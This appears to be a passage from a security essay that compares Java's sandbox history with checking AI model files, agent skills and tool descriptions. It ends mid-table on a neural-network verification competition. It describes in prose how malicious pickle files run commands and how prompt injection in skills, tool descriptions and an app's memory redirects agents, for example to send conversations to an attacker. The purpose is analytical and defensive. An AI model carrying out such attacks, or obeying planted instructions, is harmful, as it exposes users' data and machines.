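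### What the published attacks had in common

In *An In-Depth Study of More Than Ten Years of Java Exploitation* (2016), Holzinger, Triller and colleagues looked for the weaknesses that attackers had used. They collected 87 exploits (programs that take advantage of a security flaw) from public databases, security tools and a research company. Most targeted Oracle's version of Java, and the flaws with official identifiers dated from 2003 to 2013.

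They ran each exploit in an isolated environment. For exploits meant to escape Java's restrictions, their test program switched on the default Security Manager, ran the exploit and checked whether the Security Manager was still in place. They discarded exploits that failed, cut the others down to the essential lines and merged any that did the same thing in the same way. That left 61 exploits, of which 56 bypassed Java's protection completely, three disclosed information and two made the system unavailable.

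The table shows the weaknesses that they identified. One exploit could use several of them.

| Weakness | Exploits, out of 61 |
|---|---|
| Use of restricted internal classes | 32 |
| Loading of classes that should have been out of reach | 31 |
| Creation of a new class with full permissions | 31 |
| Access to hidden fields and methods through reflection | 28 |
| Confused deputies | 22 |
| Methods that adapt to their immediate caller | 22 |
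| Use of method handles | 21 |
| Serialization flaws and type confusion | 9 |
| Running the attacker's code with the library's privileges | 7 |

Reflection lets a running program look up classes, fields and methods by name, and method handles are a newer feature with a similar purpose. Both have legitimate uses, such as in testing tools, but they can also bypass the restrictions on private fields. Serialization turns objects into bytes for storage, and an attacker who edits the bytes can produce an object in a state that no ordinary program could create.

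Restricted classes are internal parts of the library that application code was not supposed to load. Many could be used to switch off the permission checks. Java protected them mainly by preventing applications from obtaining them, so a program that did obtain one could usually use it without further checks. The list of packages that needed this protection grew from 4 in the first release of Java 7 to 47 in a 2016 release of Java 8. Holzinger and colleagues consider this growth a dangerous trend.

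In 20 of the 31 exploits that loaded forbidden classes, the attacker got a trusted library class to make the request. This worked because some library methods checked only their immediate caller, not the whole call stack, and behaved differently if that caller was trusted. One of them, Java's usual method for loading a class by name, passed the request to the loader that had defined the calling class. A request from an application class therefore went to the application's loader, which was supposed to refuse restricted classes, but a request from a library class went to the bootstrap class loader, which could load anything in the core library.

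An attacker therefore needed only a library class that would pass on a request the attacker chose. The bootstrap class loader then supplied the correct class, with no way to detect that the name had come from an applet. The other 11 exploits got their classes through various other flaws. In one case, a trusted class offered a public way to load any class without restriction.

Most of the library methods that served as deputies had never explicitly raised their privileges on a caller's behalf. Seven exploits ran the attacker's code with the library's full privileges. Only four of those, all in IBM's version of Java, relied on a library class that had explicitly raised its privileges. More than 20 exploits relied on privileges that a method automatically gave its immediate caller. Holzinger and colleagues take this as a sign that privileges are easier to control when programmers have to ask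 for them, though they want more studies before drawing a firm conclusion. A programmer who calls doPrivileged presumably knows that the next few lines need care, but someone who writes an ordinary helper method may not know that it has any special privileges.

Many exploits also needed several flaws at once. Of the 61 exploits, 31 followed some version of the same sequence, which was to load a restricted class, gain access to its methods and then call them. In 22 of these, at least one step relied on a confused deputy combined with a method that trusted its immediate caller. Changing the methods that trusted their immediate caller would have stopped all 22. Safer alternatives already existed for some of these methods, but removing the originals would have broken existing programs.

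Vendors often blocked one route of attack without fixing the underlying weakness. Attackers could then replace the blocked step with a similar one and keep the rest of the exploit. One exploit for a 2013 flaw in Java 7 still worked, with minor changes, on a much later release of Java 8.

The numbers come from a collection of exploits, so they don't measure how often criminals used each one. One company, Security Explorations, supplied 52 of the original 87, so its researchers' interests must have influenced the totals. But every exploit in the final set worked, so the collection is good evidence of the kinds of mistake that existed.

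### Permitted steps with a forbidden result

A permission system can also fail when every check is correct. OpenJDK reports that some Java permissions let a program use a series of safe operations to achieve an effect that would require a more powerful permission if requested directly.

Suppose a policy lets a program write to any file but forbids it to open network connections. Java could read its policy from a file on the same disk. The program could add a line to that file giving itself network access, and the new rule would apply the next time the program started. The policy allows this because it is an ordinary write to a file. To prevent it, whoever writes the policy has to realise that permission to write to any file is, in effect, permission to do everything else.

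Stack inspection was poorly suited to catching such sequences because it considered only the calls in progress during the check. For example, a program might ask an untrusted plug-in for the name of a temporary file and then delete that file. If the plug-in returns the name of an important document instead, its method has finished and left the stack by the time the program deletes the document, so the check ignores the plug-in's lack of permission. Three of the exploits that Holzinger and colleagues studied used a related gap by getting trusted classes to run the attacker's instructions later, when every class on the stack was trusted.

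Abadi and Fournet proposed checking the permissions of methods that had already finished as well as those still running. This would catch the plug-in, but it would also refuse many harmless operations, because any untrusted code that had run earlier could cause a refusal, even if that code had nothing to do with the file. Pistoia and colleagues therefore suggested checking only the methods responsible for the operation. That requires tracking how information moves through a program, which is much harder than reading the call stack.

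### Why Java gave up on its sandbox

A sandbox lets some code run with fewer permissions than other code. By 2021, Java's original reason for having one had almost disappeared. Oracle's own Java release had dropped its browser plug-in for applets in 2018, and few people used the Security Manager for anything else.

Much of the difficulty was in writing a policy. Java offered no way to allow everything except one operation, so a developer who wanted to restrict only one thing, such as which directory a program could read, had to list every other permission the program needed. If the developer missed one, a legitimate part of the program would fail.

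Libraries made this harder because Java checked every class on the call stack. A permission that a library needed usually had to go to the application that called it too, even if the application had no use for it. The library's developer could avoid this by marking the call as privileged, but doing so safely required more knowledge of security than most developers had. It was easier to grant every permission to all code. According to Mullan and Buckley, most of the few applications that switched the Security Manager on did this, and so got almost no protection from it.

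The checks were also slow, and they had always been off by default for programs started from the command line. OpenJDK could name only a handful of products that came with their own policy files, including the search engine Elasticsearch and the web server Tomcat.

The maintainers still had to support the system. In 2024, Mullan and Buckley counted over 1,000 library methods that had to check permissions and over 1,200 that had to raise their own privileges to work for callers that had few. An attacker could exploit a forgotten check in the first group or use a careless method in the second as a confused deputy. OpenJDK's developers had to review every change to these methods, and they had about 4,000 tests for the Security Manager. Disabling the Security Manager would let them delete over 50,000 lines of code, including tests, which is close to the size of the JDK's whole type-safety base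 in 2002.

Meanwhile, the threats had changed, and most attacks on Java programs now came through malicious data sent to trusted code, much as a prompt injection reaches an agent. For example, an attacker might send a document that makes the program contact a hostile server. The program has permission to use the network, so a permission check allows the request. OpenJDK estimated that the Security Manager could not address 19 of the 25 most dangerous kinds of software weakness on a 2020 industry list. Java's developers preferred to work on defences that examine the data itself, such as the filters Java 9 introduced to reject serialized objects before the program rebuilds them.

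Java 17, released in 2021, marked the Security Manager for removal, and programs that used it began to print warnings. Mullan and Buckley saw hardly any discussion of these warnings, which they took as confirmation that few people depended on the Security Manager. Java 24 disabled it permanently.

### What replaced it

Nothing in Java does the same job. OpenJDK recommends two other kinds of protection, one inside the JVM and one outside it.

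Java now enforces the boundaries between modules more strictly, so that application code can't reach the library's internal classes. In 2016, Holzinger and colleagues suggested that the module system, then in development, might protect these classes better than the list of restricted packages, but they wanted a thorough security analysis first. Module boundaries don't control whether a program may read a particular file.

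That decision is now left to tools outside the JVM. A container gives a program its own restricted view of the operating system's files and network. A hypervisor isolates the program further by running a complete operating system inside a simulated computer. Operating systems also have their own ways to limit a program, such as the macOS App Sandbox and Linux's seccomp, which restricts the requests a program can make to the operating system. Mullan and Buckley argue that these tools are easier to learn than the Security Manager and far more widely used.

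However, they work on whole programs. The Security Manager could, in theory, give two libraries in the same program different permissions. A container gives both libraries the same access because they run in the same process. Giving them different permissions requires splitting the program into separate processes and controlling what passes between them.

Some developers had used the Security Manager for a smaller purpose, such as preventing a plug-in from shutting down the whole application. OpenJDK's developers built and tested several possible replacements for this use, but found that people wanted too many different things from them. They now suggest rewriting the plug-in's code as the JVM loads it, so that it never makes the forbidden call. The Security Manager had never reliably blocked such calls from hostile code, which, according to Mullan and Buckley, had countless ways to avoid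 interception.

Java 24 removed the Security Manager's working parts, as OpenJDK's *Implement JEP 486* records, but kept its outer classes and methods so that older libraries would still run. Depending on the method, a call now returns an empty result, carries out the request unchecked, or fails with an error, according to Oracle's *The Security Manager Is Permanently Disabled*. For Java 25, OpenJDK's *Deprecate core library permission classes for removal* also marked for removal the classes that represent individual permissions, such as permission to use a file.

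In January 2026 a developer asked about the removal of AccessControlException, one of the remaining Security Manager classes, because a frozen interface depended on it. Mullan (2026), in *removal of AccessControlException vs javax.jcr*, replied that OpenJDK had not removed the class yet but planned to do so eventually. OpenJDK's *Class SecurityManager*, part of the Java 26 documentation, still describes the main class and notes that it has no replacement. Inside Java's *The Arrival of Java 27!* (2026) lists nine major changes in the September release, and removing the Security Manager's classes is not among them, so they are probably still in Java 27, although they no longer protect anything.

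### Did the small core fail, or the library around it?

Java's trusted core had faults. Saraswat, and later Coglio and Goldberg, broke type safety by exploiting disagreements between loaders about what a name meant. But only 4 of the 61 exploits in the 2016 study used type confusion. In the 20 cases where a trusted class requested a forbidden class for an attacker, a perfect loader and verifier would not have stopped the attack. This history is therefore not enough to conclude that a small trusted core can't confine hostile code.

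The evidence fits better with the view that the small core mostly held and the large library around it failed. It doesn't prove this, because attackers usually take the easiest route, and few may have attacked the verifier when the library offered so many easier targets. Code size also seems to have been a poor guide to where the problems would be. In Appel and Wang's count, HotSpot's compiler group was about seven times as large as the library part of the trusted base, yet most of the exploits began in the library. The comparison is loose because the library had grown a great deal by the time of those exploits. But an attacker could call library methods directly and choose their arguments, which matters more than the number of lines.

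Java's design shares the blame with its library. By Appel and Wang's test, any library code whose bugs could break security was part of the trusted base. Java put much of the library in that base by giving full permissions to every class the bootstrap class loader loaded, whether or not the class needed them. For example, a class for handling dates had the same access to the disk as the classes that manage files.

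Java never had a small reference monitor for its permissions. The verifier was a single component with one job, but the permission system depended on more than a thousand methods each requesting a check, and on others not letting the wrong caller use their privileges. It could not meet Anderson's requirement that the checker be small enough to analyse completely, and some methods let their callers skip the full check.

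An AI core could repeat this mistake even if its loader were small and free of bugs. For example, the core might pass approved requests to a mail tool that can read every mailbox in a company. If the tool doesn't check which mailboxes the agent may read, it is a confused deputy, and its code belongs in the trusted base along with the core's. The same is true of any other tool that acts with more authority than the agent calling it.

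## What can a loader check in a model file or an agent's add-ons?

Like Java, an AI core would start with bytes that someone else supplied. A loader can determine a lot about a model file, including whether opening it can run code, whether anyone has altered it, and who released it. It can determine much less about the written instructions that extend an agent, because their effect depends on how a language model interprets them.

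### What an AI system loads

Java code normally arrives as class files, so one verifier can check nearly all of it. An AI system has no such common format. Before an agent does any work, it may load:

- the model's weights
- adapters, which are small sets of extra weights that adjust a model for a narrower job, such as answering medical questions
- model code, the library that arranges the weights into a network and does the arithmetic
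- tool descriptions, short texts that tell the model what each tool does and how to call it
- skills, which package instructions and scripts for a particular task

Model code is ordinary software, so developers can review it and pin its version as they would with any other library. Weights and written instructions need separate checks.

### Model files that run code when opened

The closest literal parallel to class loading is pickle, Python's built-in format for saving objects to a file. Machine-learning libraries adopted it because it can save almost anything. As *PickleBall* (Kellas, Li and colleagues, 2025) explains, a pickle file is a small program for a stack-based machine inside Python. It is similar to a class file, which contains bytecodes for the JVM. Some pickle instructions create plain values such as numbers. Others name a Python function or class, which Python then imports,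 and another calls the function with arguments from the file.

Libraries have legitimate uses for this. When a program saves a tensor (a grid of numbers that holds some of the model's weights), the library may record the name of the function that rebuilds it. An attacker can instead write `os.system`, the function that runs an operating-system command, followed by a command that steals the user's passwords. Python runs the command while opening the file, before the user runs the model.

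The JVM also looks up names it finds in a file, but it runs none of a class's code until it has verified the whole class. Pickle has no verifier, and Python calls the functions named in a pickle file as it reaches them. The attacker doesn't have to supply harmful code, because `os.system` is already on the victim's computer. Java's attackers similarly used powerful classes already in the standard library.

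Security researchers have warned about pickle since 2011, but it is still common. In March 2025, Kellas and colleagues looked at Hugging Face, the largest public site for sharing models. Of the repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month, 44.9% contained pickle files and about 21% offered no other format. Malicious pickle files on the site have stolen credentials and given attackers remote control of computers.

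### Forbidden names and permitted names

One defence is to scan a file for dangerous function names before opening it. The list of forbidden names is never complete, and Java's growing list of restricted packages had the same problem. The alternative is to permit only names on an approved list. Kellas and colleagues compared two tools of each kind on 84 malicious files and 252 harmless ones.

| Tool | How it decides | Malicious files stopped, out of 84 | Harmless files accepted, out of 252 |
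|---|---|---|---|
| ModelScan | List of forbidden names | 75 | 236 |
| ModelTracer | Loads the file and watches for a few dangerous operations | 44 | 252 |
| PyTorch's weights-only mode | One fixed list of permitted names | 84 | 157 |
| PickleBall | A separate list of permitted names for each library | 84 | 201 |

ModelScan missed five malicious files because they called functions that were not on its list. It missed three more because they used an ordinary function to load a second file containing the attack. ModelTracer checks for operations such as opening a network connection, so it missed files that read or wrote sensitive data.

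Lists of permitted names stopped every attack but also blocked many harmless files. PyTorch, the main library for building models, now uses its weights-only mode by default. In a separate sample of 1,426 popular repositories that offered only pickle files, 15.4% contained at least one model that this mode could not load. Because of such failures, the developers of flair, a text-analysis library, turned the protection off in their own loading code. Most applications that used Java's Security Manager had similarly granted every permission.

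PickleBall reduces the problem by using each library's source code to list the names that a file may import and those that it may call. Suppose a library's Model class contains a Tensor, which uses a function called `read_weights` to rebuild itself. PickleBall starts at Model and adds it to the import list. It then follows the reference to Tensor, finds `read_weights`, and adds that function to both lists. Nothing in Model leads to `os.system`, so it appears on neither list.

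PickleBall replaces Python's usual loader when the user opens a file. If the file refers to an unlisted name, PickleBall inserts an inert placeholder and raises an error only if the program tries to use it. A model can still load if the unlisted item is leftover data from training. Making a list took a median of 14 seconds per library, and enforcing it added about 2% to the loading time. Of the 51 harmless files that PickleBall rejected, 44 came from two image-recognition libraries whose files did not refer to functions by consistent names.

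The perfect scores against malicious files call for some caution. Other researchers' scanners had already found 82 of the 84 files, and Kellas and colleagues built the other two to get past scanners rather than lists of permitted names. PickleBall's lists also let a file call about 61 functions, although the models from most of the libraries called only two. An attacker might be able to combine permitted functions to do something harmful, as Java programs sometimes could with permitted operations. Kellas and colleagues know of no such attack, but they don't rule one out.

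A list of permitted names also works only if the loader enforces it correctly. OSV's *CVE-2025-32434* (2025), an entry in a public database of software flaws, describes how a malicious file could run commands on a user's computer even in PyTorch's weights-only mode. The flaw, which scored 9.3 out of 10 for severity, affected versions up to 2.5.1, and PyTorch fixed it in 2.6.0. Ji'an Zhou, who found it, noted in the advisory text on Docker Scout's *CVE-2025-32434* page that PyTorch's documentation had treated this mode as safe. Like Java's verifier, the weights-only loader was part of the trusted base, and users had relied on it to open files from strangers.

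Safetensors, a format that Hugging Face released in 2022, has no place for function names. A safetensors file has a header listing the name, number type and shape of each tensor, followed by the numbers. The loader has no functions to look up and no instructions to follow, so it can be much simpler than a pickle loader, and independent auditors have examined it. But publishers often leave the old pickle file next to the safetensors file, and people who adapt a large language model sometimes add a pickle file of their training settings. A core would therefore have to refuse pickle outright, even when most of a model is in safetensors.

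### Hashes, signatures and provenance records

A file in a safe format can still be the wrong file, so a loader can also check its hash. A hash is a short value that a program computes from every byte of a file, so changing a single weight changes the hash. If the loader computes the same hash that the publisher announced, it has the publisher's file. However, an attacker who can replace a file on a website may be able to replace the announced hash too.

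A signature links the hash to an identity. The publisher signs the hash with a private key, and anyone with the matching public key can check it. This matters because, as OpenSSF (the Open Source Security Foundation) notes, the team that trains a large model is usually not the one that uses it. Maruseac, Sablotny and colleagues (2025) announced the foundation's common tool for signing models of any size and format in *Launch of Model Signing v1.0*. NVIDIA has begun to adopt the standard in its model catalogue, according to HiddenLayer, a security company that helps lead the project.

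Publishers can sign models with their own keys or through Sigstore, a service that links a signature to an online account. In an example from Sigstore's *Taming the Wild West of ML*, the user verifying a model must state whose signature to expect. A valid signature from an unknown account gives little assurance, so a core would need its own list of which publishers may supply which models.

Google (2023) gives PoisonGPT as an example of an attack that signatures would expose. Researchers altered an open model to repeat a false claim and published it under a name close to the original developer's. With signing, the altered copy would either fail the check or be traceable to whoever altered it. The check would not reveal a false claim that the original developer had trained into the model. Red Hat's *Model authenticity and transparency with Sigstore* (2025) says verification confirms that a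 model is exactly what its creators intended, which is slightly too strong. Verification confirms that the file is the one they released, but they may not know everything the model learned in training.

A provenance record describes how someone produced a file. Google recommends SLSA, a specification for such records in conventional software. *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025), from the industry's Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI), works towards tamper-proof records for models. A record might list the training data, the training code and the starting model, each with its hash. If a dataset turned out to contain planted material, a company could use these records to find every model trained on it. The records are hard to check independently, though. Anyone with a Java program's source code can recompile it and compare the results, but retraining a large model is very expensive and may not produce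 the same weights.

### One model file in an ideal loader

Suppose a hospital wants to load a model that summarises patients' notes. The publisher has supplied a safetensors file, a signature and a description of the network. An ideal loader would check the following:

1. Format. The file must be in safetensors, whatever its name suggests. The loader refuses pickle.
2. Hash. The file's hash must match the one that the hospital recorded when it approved the model.
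3. Signature. The expected publisher must have signed that hash.
4. Tensor shapes. The tensors must fit the description of the network. If the description calls for a grid of 4,096 by 4,096 numbers at two bytes each, that tensor must take up exactly 33,554,432 bytes. No tensor may overlap another or run past the end of the file.
5. Permitted operators. The description may use only approved operations, such as adding and multiplying grids of numbers. This check matters most for formats that store the operations in the model file itself, such as ONNX and TensorFlow's SavedModel. Kellas and colleagues note that both allow some operations that an attacker could abuse in certain settings, though nobody has reported a real attack.

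If every check passes, the hospital knows that it has the file it approved, that the file came from the expected publisher, and that the model can only do arithmetic on arrays of the right shapes. The last guarantee is close to type safety. The model cannot open a file or a network connection unless the surrounding software does so for it.

The hospital still doesn't know whether the summaries will be accurate. A file of random numbers with the same shapes or a model with a hidden backdoor would pass the checks on format, shapes and operators. Either would also pass the other two checks if the publisher had signed it and the hospital had approved it.

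A loader should also check that an adapter is paired with the model it was trained on. The adapter's tensors will fit any model with the right shapes, but its numbers are useful only with that one. If the hospital replaced the model with another of the same shape, the adapter would still load, and the combination might behave in untested ways. Saraswat's attack on Java similarly worked because the JVM treated two different classes as the same when their names matched. An adapter's provenance record should therefore include the hash of its model, so that the loader can reject any other.

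### Malicious skills and tool servers

An agent follows a skill's instructions and runs its scripts with whatever access it has to the user's computer. People share skills through public registries, and attackers have been uploading malicious ones since shortly after the registries opened.

Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Do Not Mention This to the User*, examined 98,380 agent skills from two registries. They used pattern matching and a language model to flag 4,287 as suspicious. They ran these in isolated environments containing fake passwords and keys, and recorded which skills sent those credentials elsewhere or contacted undocumented sites. They reviewed the 762 that behaved suspiciously and confirmed that 157 were malicious. More than half of the 157 came from a single attacker who impersonated well-known brands. The registries removed all of the malicious skills.

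*MalSkills* (2026) reports 400 confirmed malicious skills among about 150,000 collected from seven registries, or about 0.3%. Of those 400, 262 came from three registries that claimed to have security checks. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) cites a much higher rate from an early audit of ClawHub, a registry for the open-source agent OpenClaw, which found 341 malicious skills among 2,857, or about 12%. One attacker can upload hundreds of nearly identical skills, so the rate depends heavily on the registry and the month.

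A loader's results also depend on what counts as malicious. In *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs*, Yang, Ying and colleagues (2026) reviewed the 157 skills that Liu and colleagues had confirmed as malicious and asked whether each skill's author had meant to harm the user. They agreed that only 95 were malicious, and judged 34 benign and the other 28 risky or unclear.

Tool descriptions can carry similar attacks. Many agents use the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard in which a separate program, called a server, offers tools and sends the agent a description of each. Koc and colleagues describe attacks in which a tool's description contains malicious instructions, or changes after the user has accepted it. A loader could store a hash of the accepted description and refuse the tool's description if it changes. It couldn't check the tool's behaviour this way if the server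 runs on someone else's computer.

### What registries check

In February 2026, after the first wave of attacks, OpenClaw began sending every new ClawHub skill to VirusTotal, a service that compares files with known malware. VirusTotal also used a language model to examine what each skill did. ClawHub approved skills that the model classified as benign, put warnings on suspicious ones, blocked malicious ones, and rescanned them all every day. OpenClaw warned that a skill could still contain malicious instructions to an agent in ordinary language, which would not match any virus signature.

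Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, found five malicious skills that had gotten through and were still available between February and May. One skill's author had added 22 megabytes of filler to a file, because many scanners skip very large files.

Since June, ClawHub has used three scanners: VirusTotal, its own pattern matching, and NVIDIA's SkillSpector, which also uses a language model to look for problems such as hidden instructions. According to OpenClaw, another language model then uses their results to classify the skill as clean, suspicious or malicious. Because this check relies on a learned model, it would not qualify as part of the proposed core. Signing was still only a proposal when Koc and colleagues described the system. Some other registries do less, and Yang and colleagues found no scanner on either of the two that Liu and colleagues had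 studied.

ClawHub's scanners rarely agree on which skills to flag. Koc and colleagues, who work for OpenClaw's foundation and NVIDIA, analysed 67,453 skills and found that 81.9% of those flagged were flagged by only one scanner. ClawHub's final verdict classed 206 skills as malicious, of which VirusTotal had flagged 150 and SkillSpector only 14. Koc and colleagues attribute the disagreement to differences in what each scanner looks for.

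That is probably part of the reason, but the scanners also miss a lot. In *After the Party*, Xiong and Zhang (2026) had two experienced reviewers judge 180 ClawHub skills without seeing the scanners' results. The scanners caught between 21.67% and 61.06% of the skills the reviewers thought needed human attention. These estimates apply to a pool of only 276 skills, and the reviewers flagged any serious concern, not just malice, so the scanners' catch rates for outright attacks could be quite different.

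### Why instructions are harder to scan than code

Java's verifier can check a method because each bytecode has a fixed meaning and a type rule. Instructions in ordinary language have neither, and an attacker can phrase the same request in many ways. Yang and colleagues tested six detectors on 886 malicious and 591 benign skills. In one set, where the attacks were mostly in ordinary language, two rule-based detectors caught only 7.5% and 11.8% of them. Adding a language model raised those rates to 96.8% and 64.5%. The best combination of detector and model across all the tests still missed 7% of the malicious skills and blocked 6.3% of the benign ones.

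Whether an instruction is harmful can also depend on facts that are not in the skill. One benign skill in these tests made phone calls through an online service. A detector blocked it for sending a secret key over the network, but the skill was only returning the key to the service that issued it, which is how such services recognise their customers. Sending the same key to another site would have been theft, even though the code could be identical except for the address.

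A strict rule would avoid some of these judgements by rejecting anything doubtful, as Java's verifier does. But skill authors, unlike Java programmers, have no compiler to keep their work within what a scanner can check, so a strict scanner rejects much of it. Yang and colleagues found that SkillSpector advised against installing 45.8% of the ClawHub skills for which they had its results.

Checking the instructions and the scripts separately leaves another gap. In *MalSkillBench*, Guo, Jia and colleagues (2026) built malicious skills and ran them to confirm that they worked. The strongest detector caught 98.4% of the attacks in code but did far worse on attacks through instructions. Some of the skills split an attack between instructions and scripts. For example, the instructions might tell the agent to download a settings file, and a script might then load it and carry out the attack. Neither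 part has to look malicious by itself, just as each class in Saraswat's attack on Java was valid by itself.

The agent also decides how to carry out the instructions. Taneja and Weber (2026), in *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action*, recorded 144 commands that an agent ran while following 39 skills, and only 2 of them appeared word for word in the skills' text. This was a small test of one agent by a start-up that develops run-time checks, but it shows how much the commands an agent runs can differ from a skill's text. An agent has much more freedom than Java's just-in-time compiler, which has to preserve what the bytecodes mean.

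Some instructions arrive after the loader has done its checks. One of the skills Unit 42 found, money-radar, offered financial advice. Its instructions were to fetch a list of products from the publisher's website every time someone used it, and to recommend them through links that earned the publisher money. The publisher could change the list without changing the skill. Agents have no equivalent of Java's verifier for new text, and Christodorescu and colleagues point out that it is often hard even to tell where an instruction came from. A loader can refuse changes to the skill itself, but protection against text that arrives later has to come from limits on what the agent can do.

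## Why can a model's behaviour not be checked at load time as a class can?

When the JVM loads a class, it checks names, types and references, but not what the class will do. It accepts an Account class that steals a tenth of every withdrawal. In general it couldn't do much better, because no checker can reliably predict what programs do. So we can't explain the difference between classes and models by saying that a class's behaviour is known before it runs and a model's is not.

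The JVM can check a class at load time because the class file declares its parts and the names its code refers to, and contains all of the class's instructions. Type safety can also be tested simply, one instruction at a time. None of this is true of a language model, so researchers have tried to prove properties of models, test them, or work out what happens inside them.

### What no checker can decide

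In 1953 the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published a proof that no procedure can correctly determine, for every program, whether the program's behaviour has a given property. The only exceptions are properties that all programs have or that none have.

No checker can correctly decide, for every program, whether it will ever delete a file. If one could, then for any program P, we could write a new program that simulates P, without letting it touch real files, and then deletes a file. The new program deletes the file only if P finishes, so the checker's verdict would reveal whether P finishes or runs forever. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can decide this for every program.

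Rice's theorem still allows a checker that makes mistakes in only one direction, as the bytecode verifier does. A checker for models could be conservative in the same way, so the theorem alone doesn't make models harder to check than classes.

In one respect, a model is easier to check than a class. It does a limited amount of arithmetic for each token (a word or piece of a word), and its input has a maximum length, so someone with unlimited time could run it on every possible input and record the results. An agent is harder to check because it can write and run its own programs, and Rice's theorem applies in full to those programs.

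Nobody has unlimited time, of course. With a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, the number of possible prompts exactly 1,000 tokens long is

100,000^1,000 = (10^5)^1,000 = 10^5,000

The observable universe contains roughly 10^80 atoms, and 1,000 tokens is only a page or two of text.

A check can be possible even when the number of inputs is huge. A Java method that adds two integers has 2^64 possible inputs, and the verifier covers them all in one pass because it checks only types. To check a property that people care about in a model, a checker would need rules that cover enormous numbers of prompts at once.

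### Weights come without declarations

According to Oracle's *The class File Format*, a class file gives the class's name, its superclass and the interfaces it implements, and describes every field and method the class declares. It also has a table, the constant pool, which holds the names of the other classes, fields and methods the code refers to. The compiler can't leave these out, because an instruction that calls a method identifies the method by its position in this table. A loader can therefore list what a class's code refers to before running any of it. This list can be incomplete, because a program that uses reflection can build a name while it runs, but the JVM still has to look that name up.

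A safetensors file has names too. A tensor might be named "layers.12.attention.query", which the model code uses to put that grid of numbers in the right place, but the name doesn't describe what the numbers are for. The file has no entry for translating French or writing malware, and either ability may depend on numbers spread over many tensors. Even the developer may not have a full list of the model's abilities, because they come from training and people often discover them by using the model.

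A developer could attach a list of abilities to a model's file, much as a skill declares its capabilities. Java's verifier can compare the StackMapTable with the instructions, but the model's loader would have nothing to compare the list with, so it would accept a false statement that the model contains no knowledge of explosives.

Permissions are hard to set at load time for a similar reason. Christodorescu and colleagues compare agents with Android apps. An app's developer builds it for a fixed set of tasks and chooses the permissions it needs, and an analyst can read the code to check whether it needs them. An agent's task arrives later, in the user's own words. A user might ask it to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a site where programmers track their work, and then to summarise the same issue. The first request needs permission to write a comment and the second needs only permission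 to read, so no list of permissions fixed at load time would fit both exactly.

### Instructions that arrive after loading

Java programs also acquire code while they run, but each new class must first go through a loader and the verifier. Christodorescu and colleagues describe browser protections for the scripts that web pages load. A page can name the sites it accepts scripts from, and the browser can refuse a script that has changed since the page's developer approved it. The browser can also isolate outside content so that it can't read the rest of the page. These protections depend on knowing where code came from and being able to confine it.

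When an agent follows new instructions, it does something like loading new code, but without a reliable form of either protection. An instruction from a web page reaches the model as tokens in the same sequence as the user's request. Developers train models to give the user's instructions priority, which works often but not always. A web page also has an owner who decides which scripts belong on it, whereas an agent's user typically gives an incomplete instruction and expects the agent to find the rest.

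A core can't just forbid agents to take instructions from what they read. Suppose an agent summarising a GitLab issue learns from the page that the issue depends on another one. It summarises both, which is probably what the user wanted. Text on a web page has changed the agent's task, just as it does in a prompt injection. Tool documentation also has to influence the agent, or the agent couldn't learn to use the tool.

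Text can steer an agent without telling it to do anything. A tool's description may include examples of how to call the tool, and an agent that copies a poisoned example will make a bad call. Christodorescu and colleagues point out that a model's output has to reflect the data it acts on. Separating instructions from data would therefore stop many attacks, but probably not all.

The effects can also outlast a single session. In an attack on ChatGPT's Mac app, a malicious document or website planted instructions in the notes that the app kept about the user. From then on, the app sent all of the user's conversations to the attacker. The attack did not change the model's weights, so checking them again would have shown nothing wrong.

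In this respect a model is more like the JVM itself than like a class. Someone could verify every line of the JVM and still know nothing about the next program it will run. Christodorescu and colleagues similarly write that a language model "represents all possible programs at once". A load-time check can examine the model but not the prompts it will later receive, which contain much of the program.

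### Harmlessness has no rule for each step

Type safety is easy to check because it is local. If every instruction in a method obeys its own type rule, the whole method passes.

Harmlessness can't be checked this way, because a dangerous model uses the same additions, multiplications and few other simple functions as a safe one. Checking whole answers isn't enough either, because the same explanation of how much paracetamol damages the liver can be useful to a nurse and to a poisoner. A strict checker could reject every model it can't prove harmless, but at present it would reject every useful language model.

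Java's designers avoided this problem by choosing a much narrower property to check and an instruction set suited to checking it. People who want to prove things about neural networks also have to choose narrow properties.

### How to prove something about a network

Neural network verification tries to prove that a network's output meets a stated condition for every input in a stated range. Take a tiny network with two inputs, x1 and x2, each between 0 and 1:

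y = ReLU(x1 − x2) + ReLU(x2 − x1)

ReLU, a common function in neural networks, leaves positive numbers unchanged and replaces negative ones with 0. Suppose we want to prove that y is never more than 1.5.

The simplest method tracks the range of each value, much as Java's verifier tracks types. The difference x1 − x2 lies between −1 and 1, so its ReLU lies between 0 and 1. The same holds for x2 − x1. Adding the two ranges gives y a range of 0 to 2, so the method can't prove the claim.

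The claim is true, though. If x1 is larger, the second ReLU is 0, and if x2 is larger, the first is 0. So y is the distance between x1 and x2, which is never more than 1. The method failed because it treated the two ReLUs as independent and allowed both to be 1 at once. Like Java's verifier, the method can reject something that is fine.

One remedy is to split the problem into cases. If x1 is at least as large as x2, the second ReLU is 0 and the first is at most 1. If x2 is larger, the first is 0 and the second is at most 1, so y is at most 1 in both cases. This works for any network built from ReLUs, but a network with n of them may need as many as 2^n cases.

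Another remedy is to track how the values relate to each other. When z = x1 − x2 is between −1 and 1, ReLU(z) is at most (z + 1)/2 and ReLU(−z) is at most (1 − z)/2. Adding the two bounds cancels z and leaves 1, so this method proves the claim without splitting. In larger networks such straight-line bounds are looser, and verification programs usually combine them with splitting.

Katz, Barrett and colleagues (2017) proved in *Reluplex* that verifying even simple properties of ReLU networks is NP-complete. This means no known method is fast on every network, and the worst cases can take exponentially long. Their own method considers a ReLU's active and inactive cases separately only when it has to, and many of the ReLUs often don't matter for the property being checked. They used it on 45 prototype networks for an aircraft collision-avoidance system. Each network had 300 ReLUs, so trying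 every combination of cases could have meant checking 2^300 of them. Among other things, they proved that a network always reports no conflict when the other aircraft is far enough away. Earlier tools had managed networks with only 10 to 20 hidden nodes.

### What the 2026 competition could verify

Researchers compare their tools in a yearly competition. Ladner, Kaulen and colleagues (2026), in *The 7th International Verification of Neural Networks Competition (VNN-COMP 2026)*, describe networks ranging from about 100 parameters to 138 million. Some examples show what the tools had to prove:

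| Network | Parameters | Property to prove |
|---|---|---|
| Aircraft collision avoidance | 13,000 | The advice is right throughout a range of positions and speeds |
| Wear of aircraft parts | 60,000–262,000 | The predicted remaining life stays within a given range |
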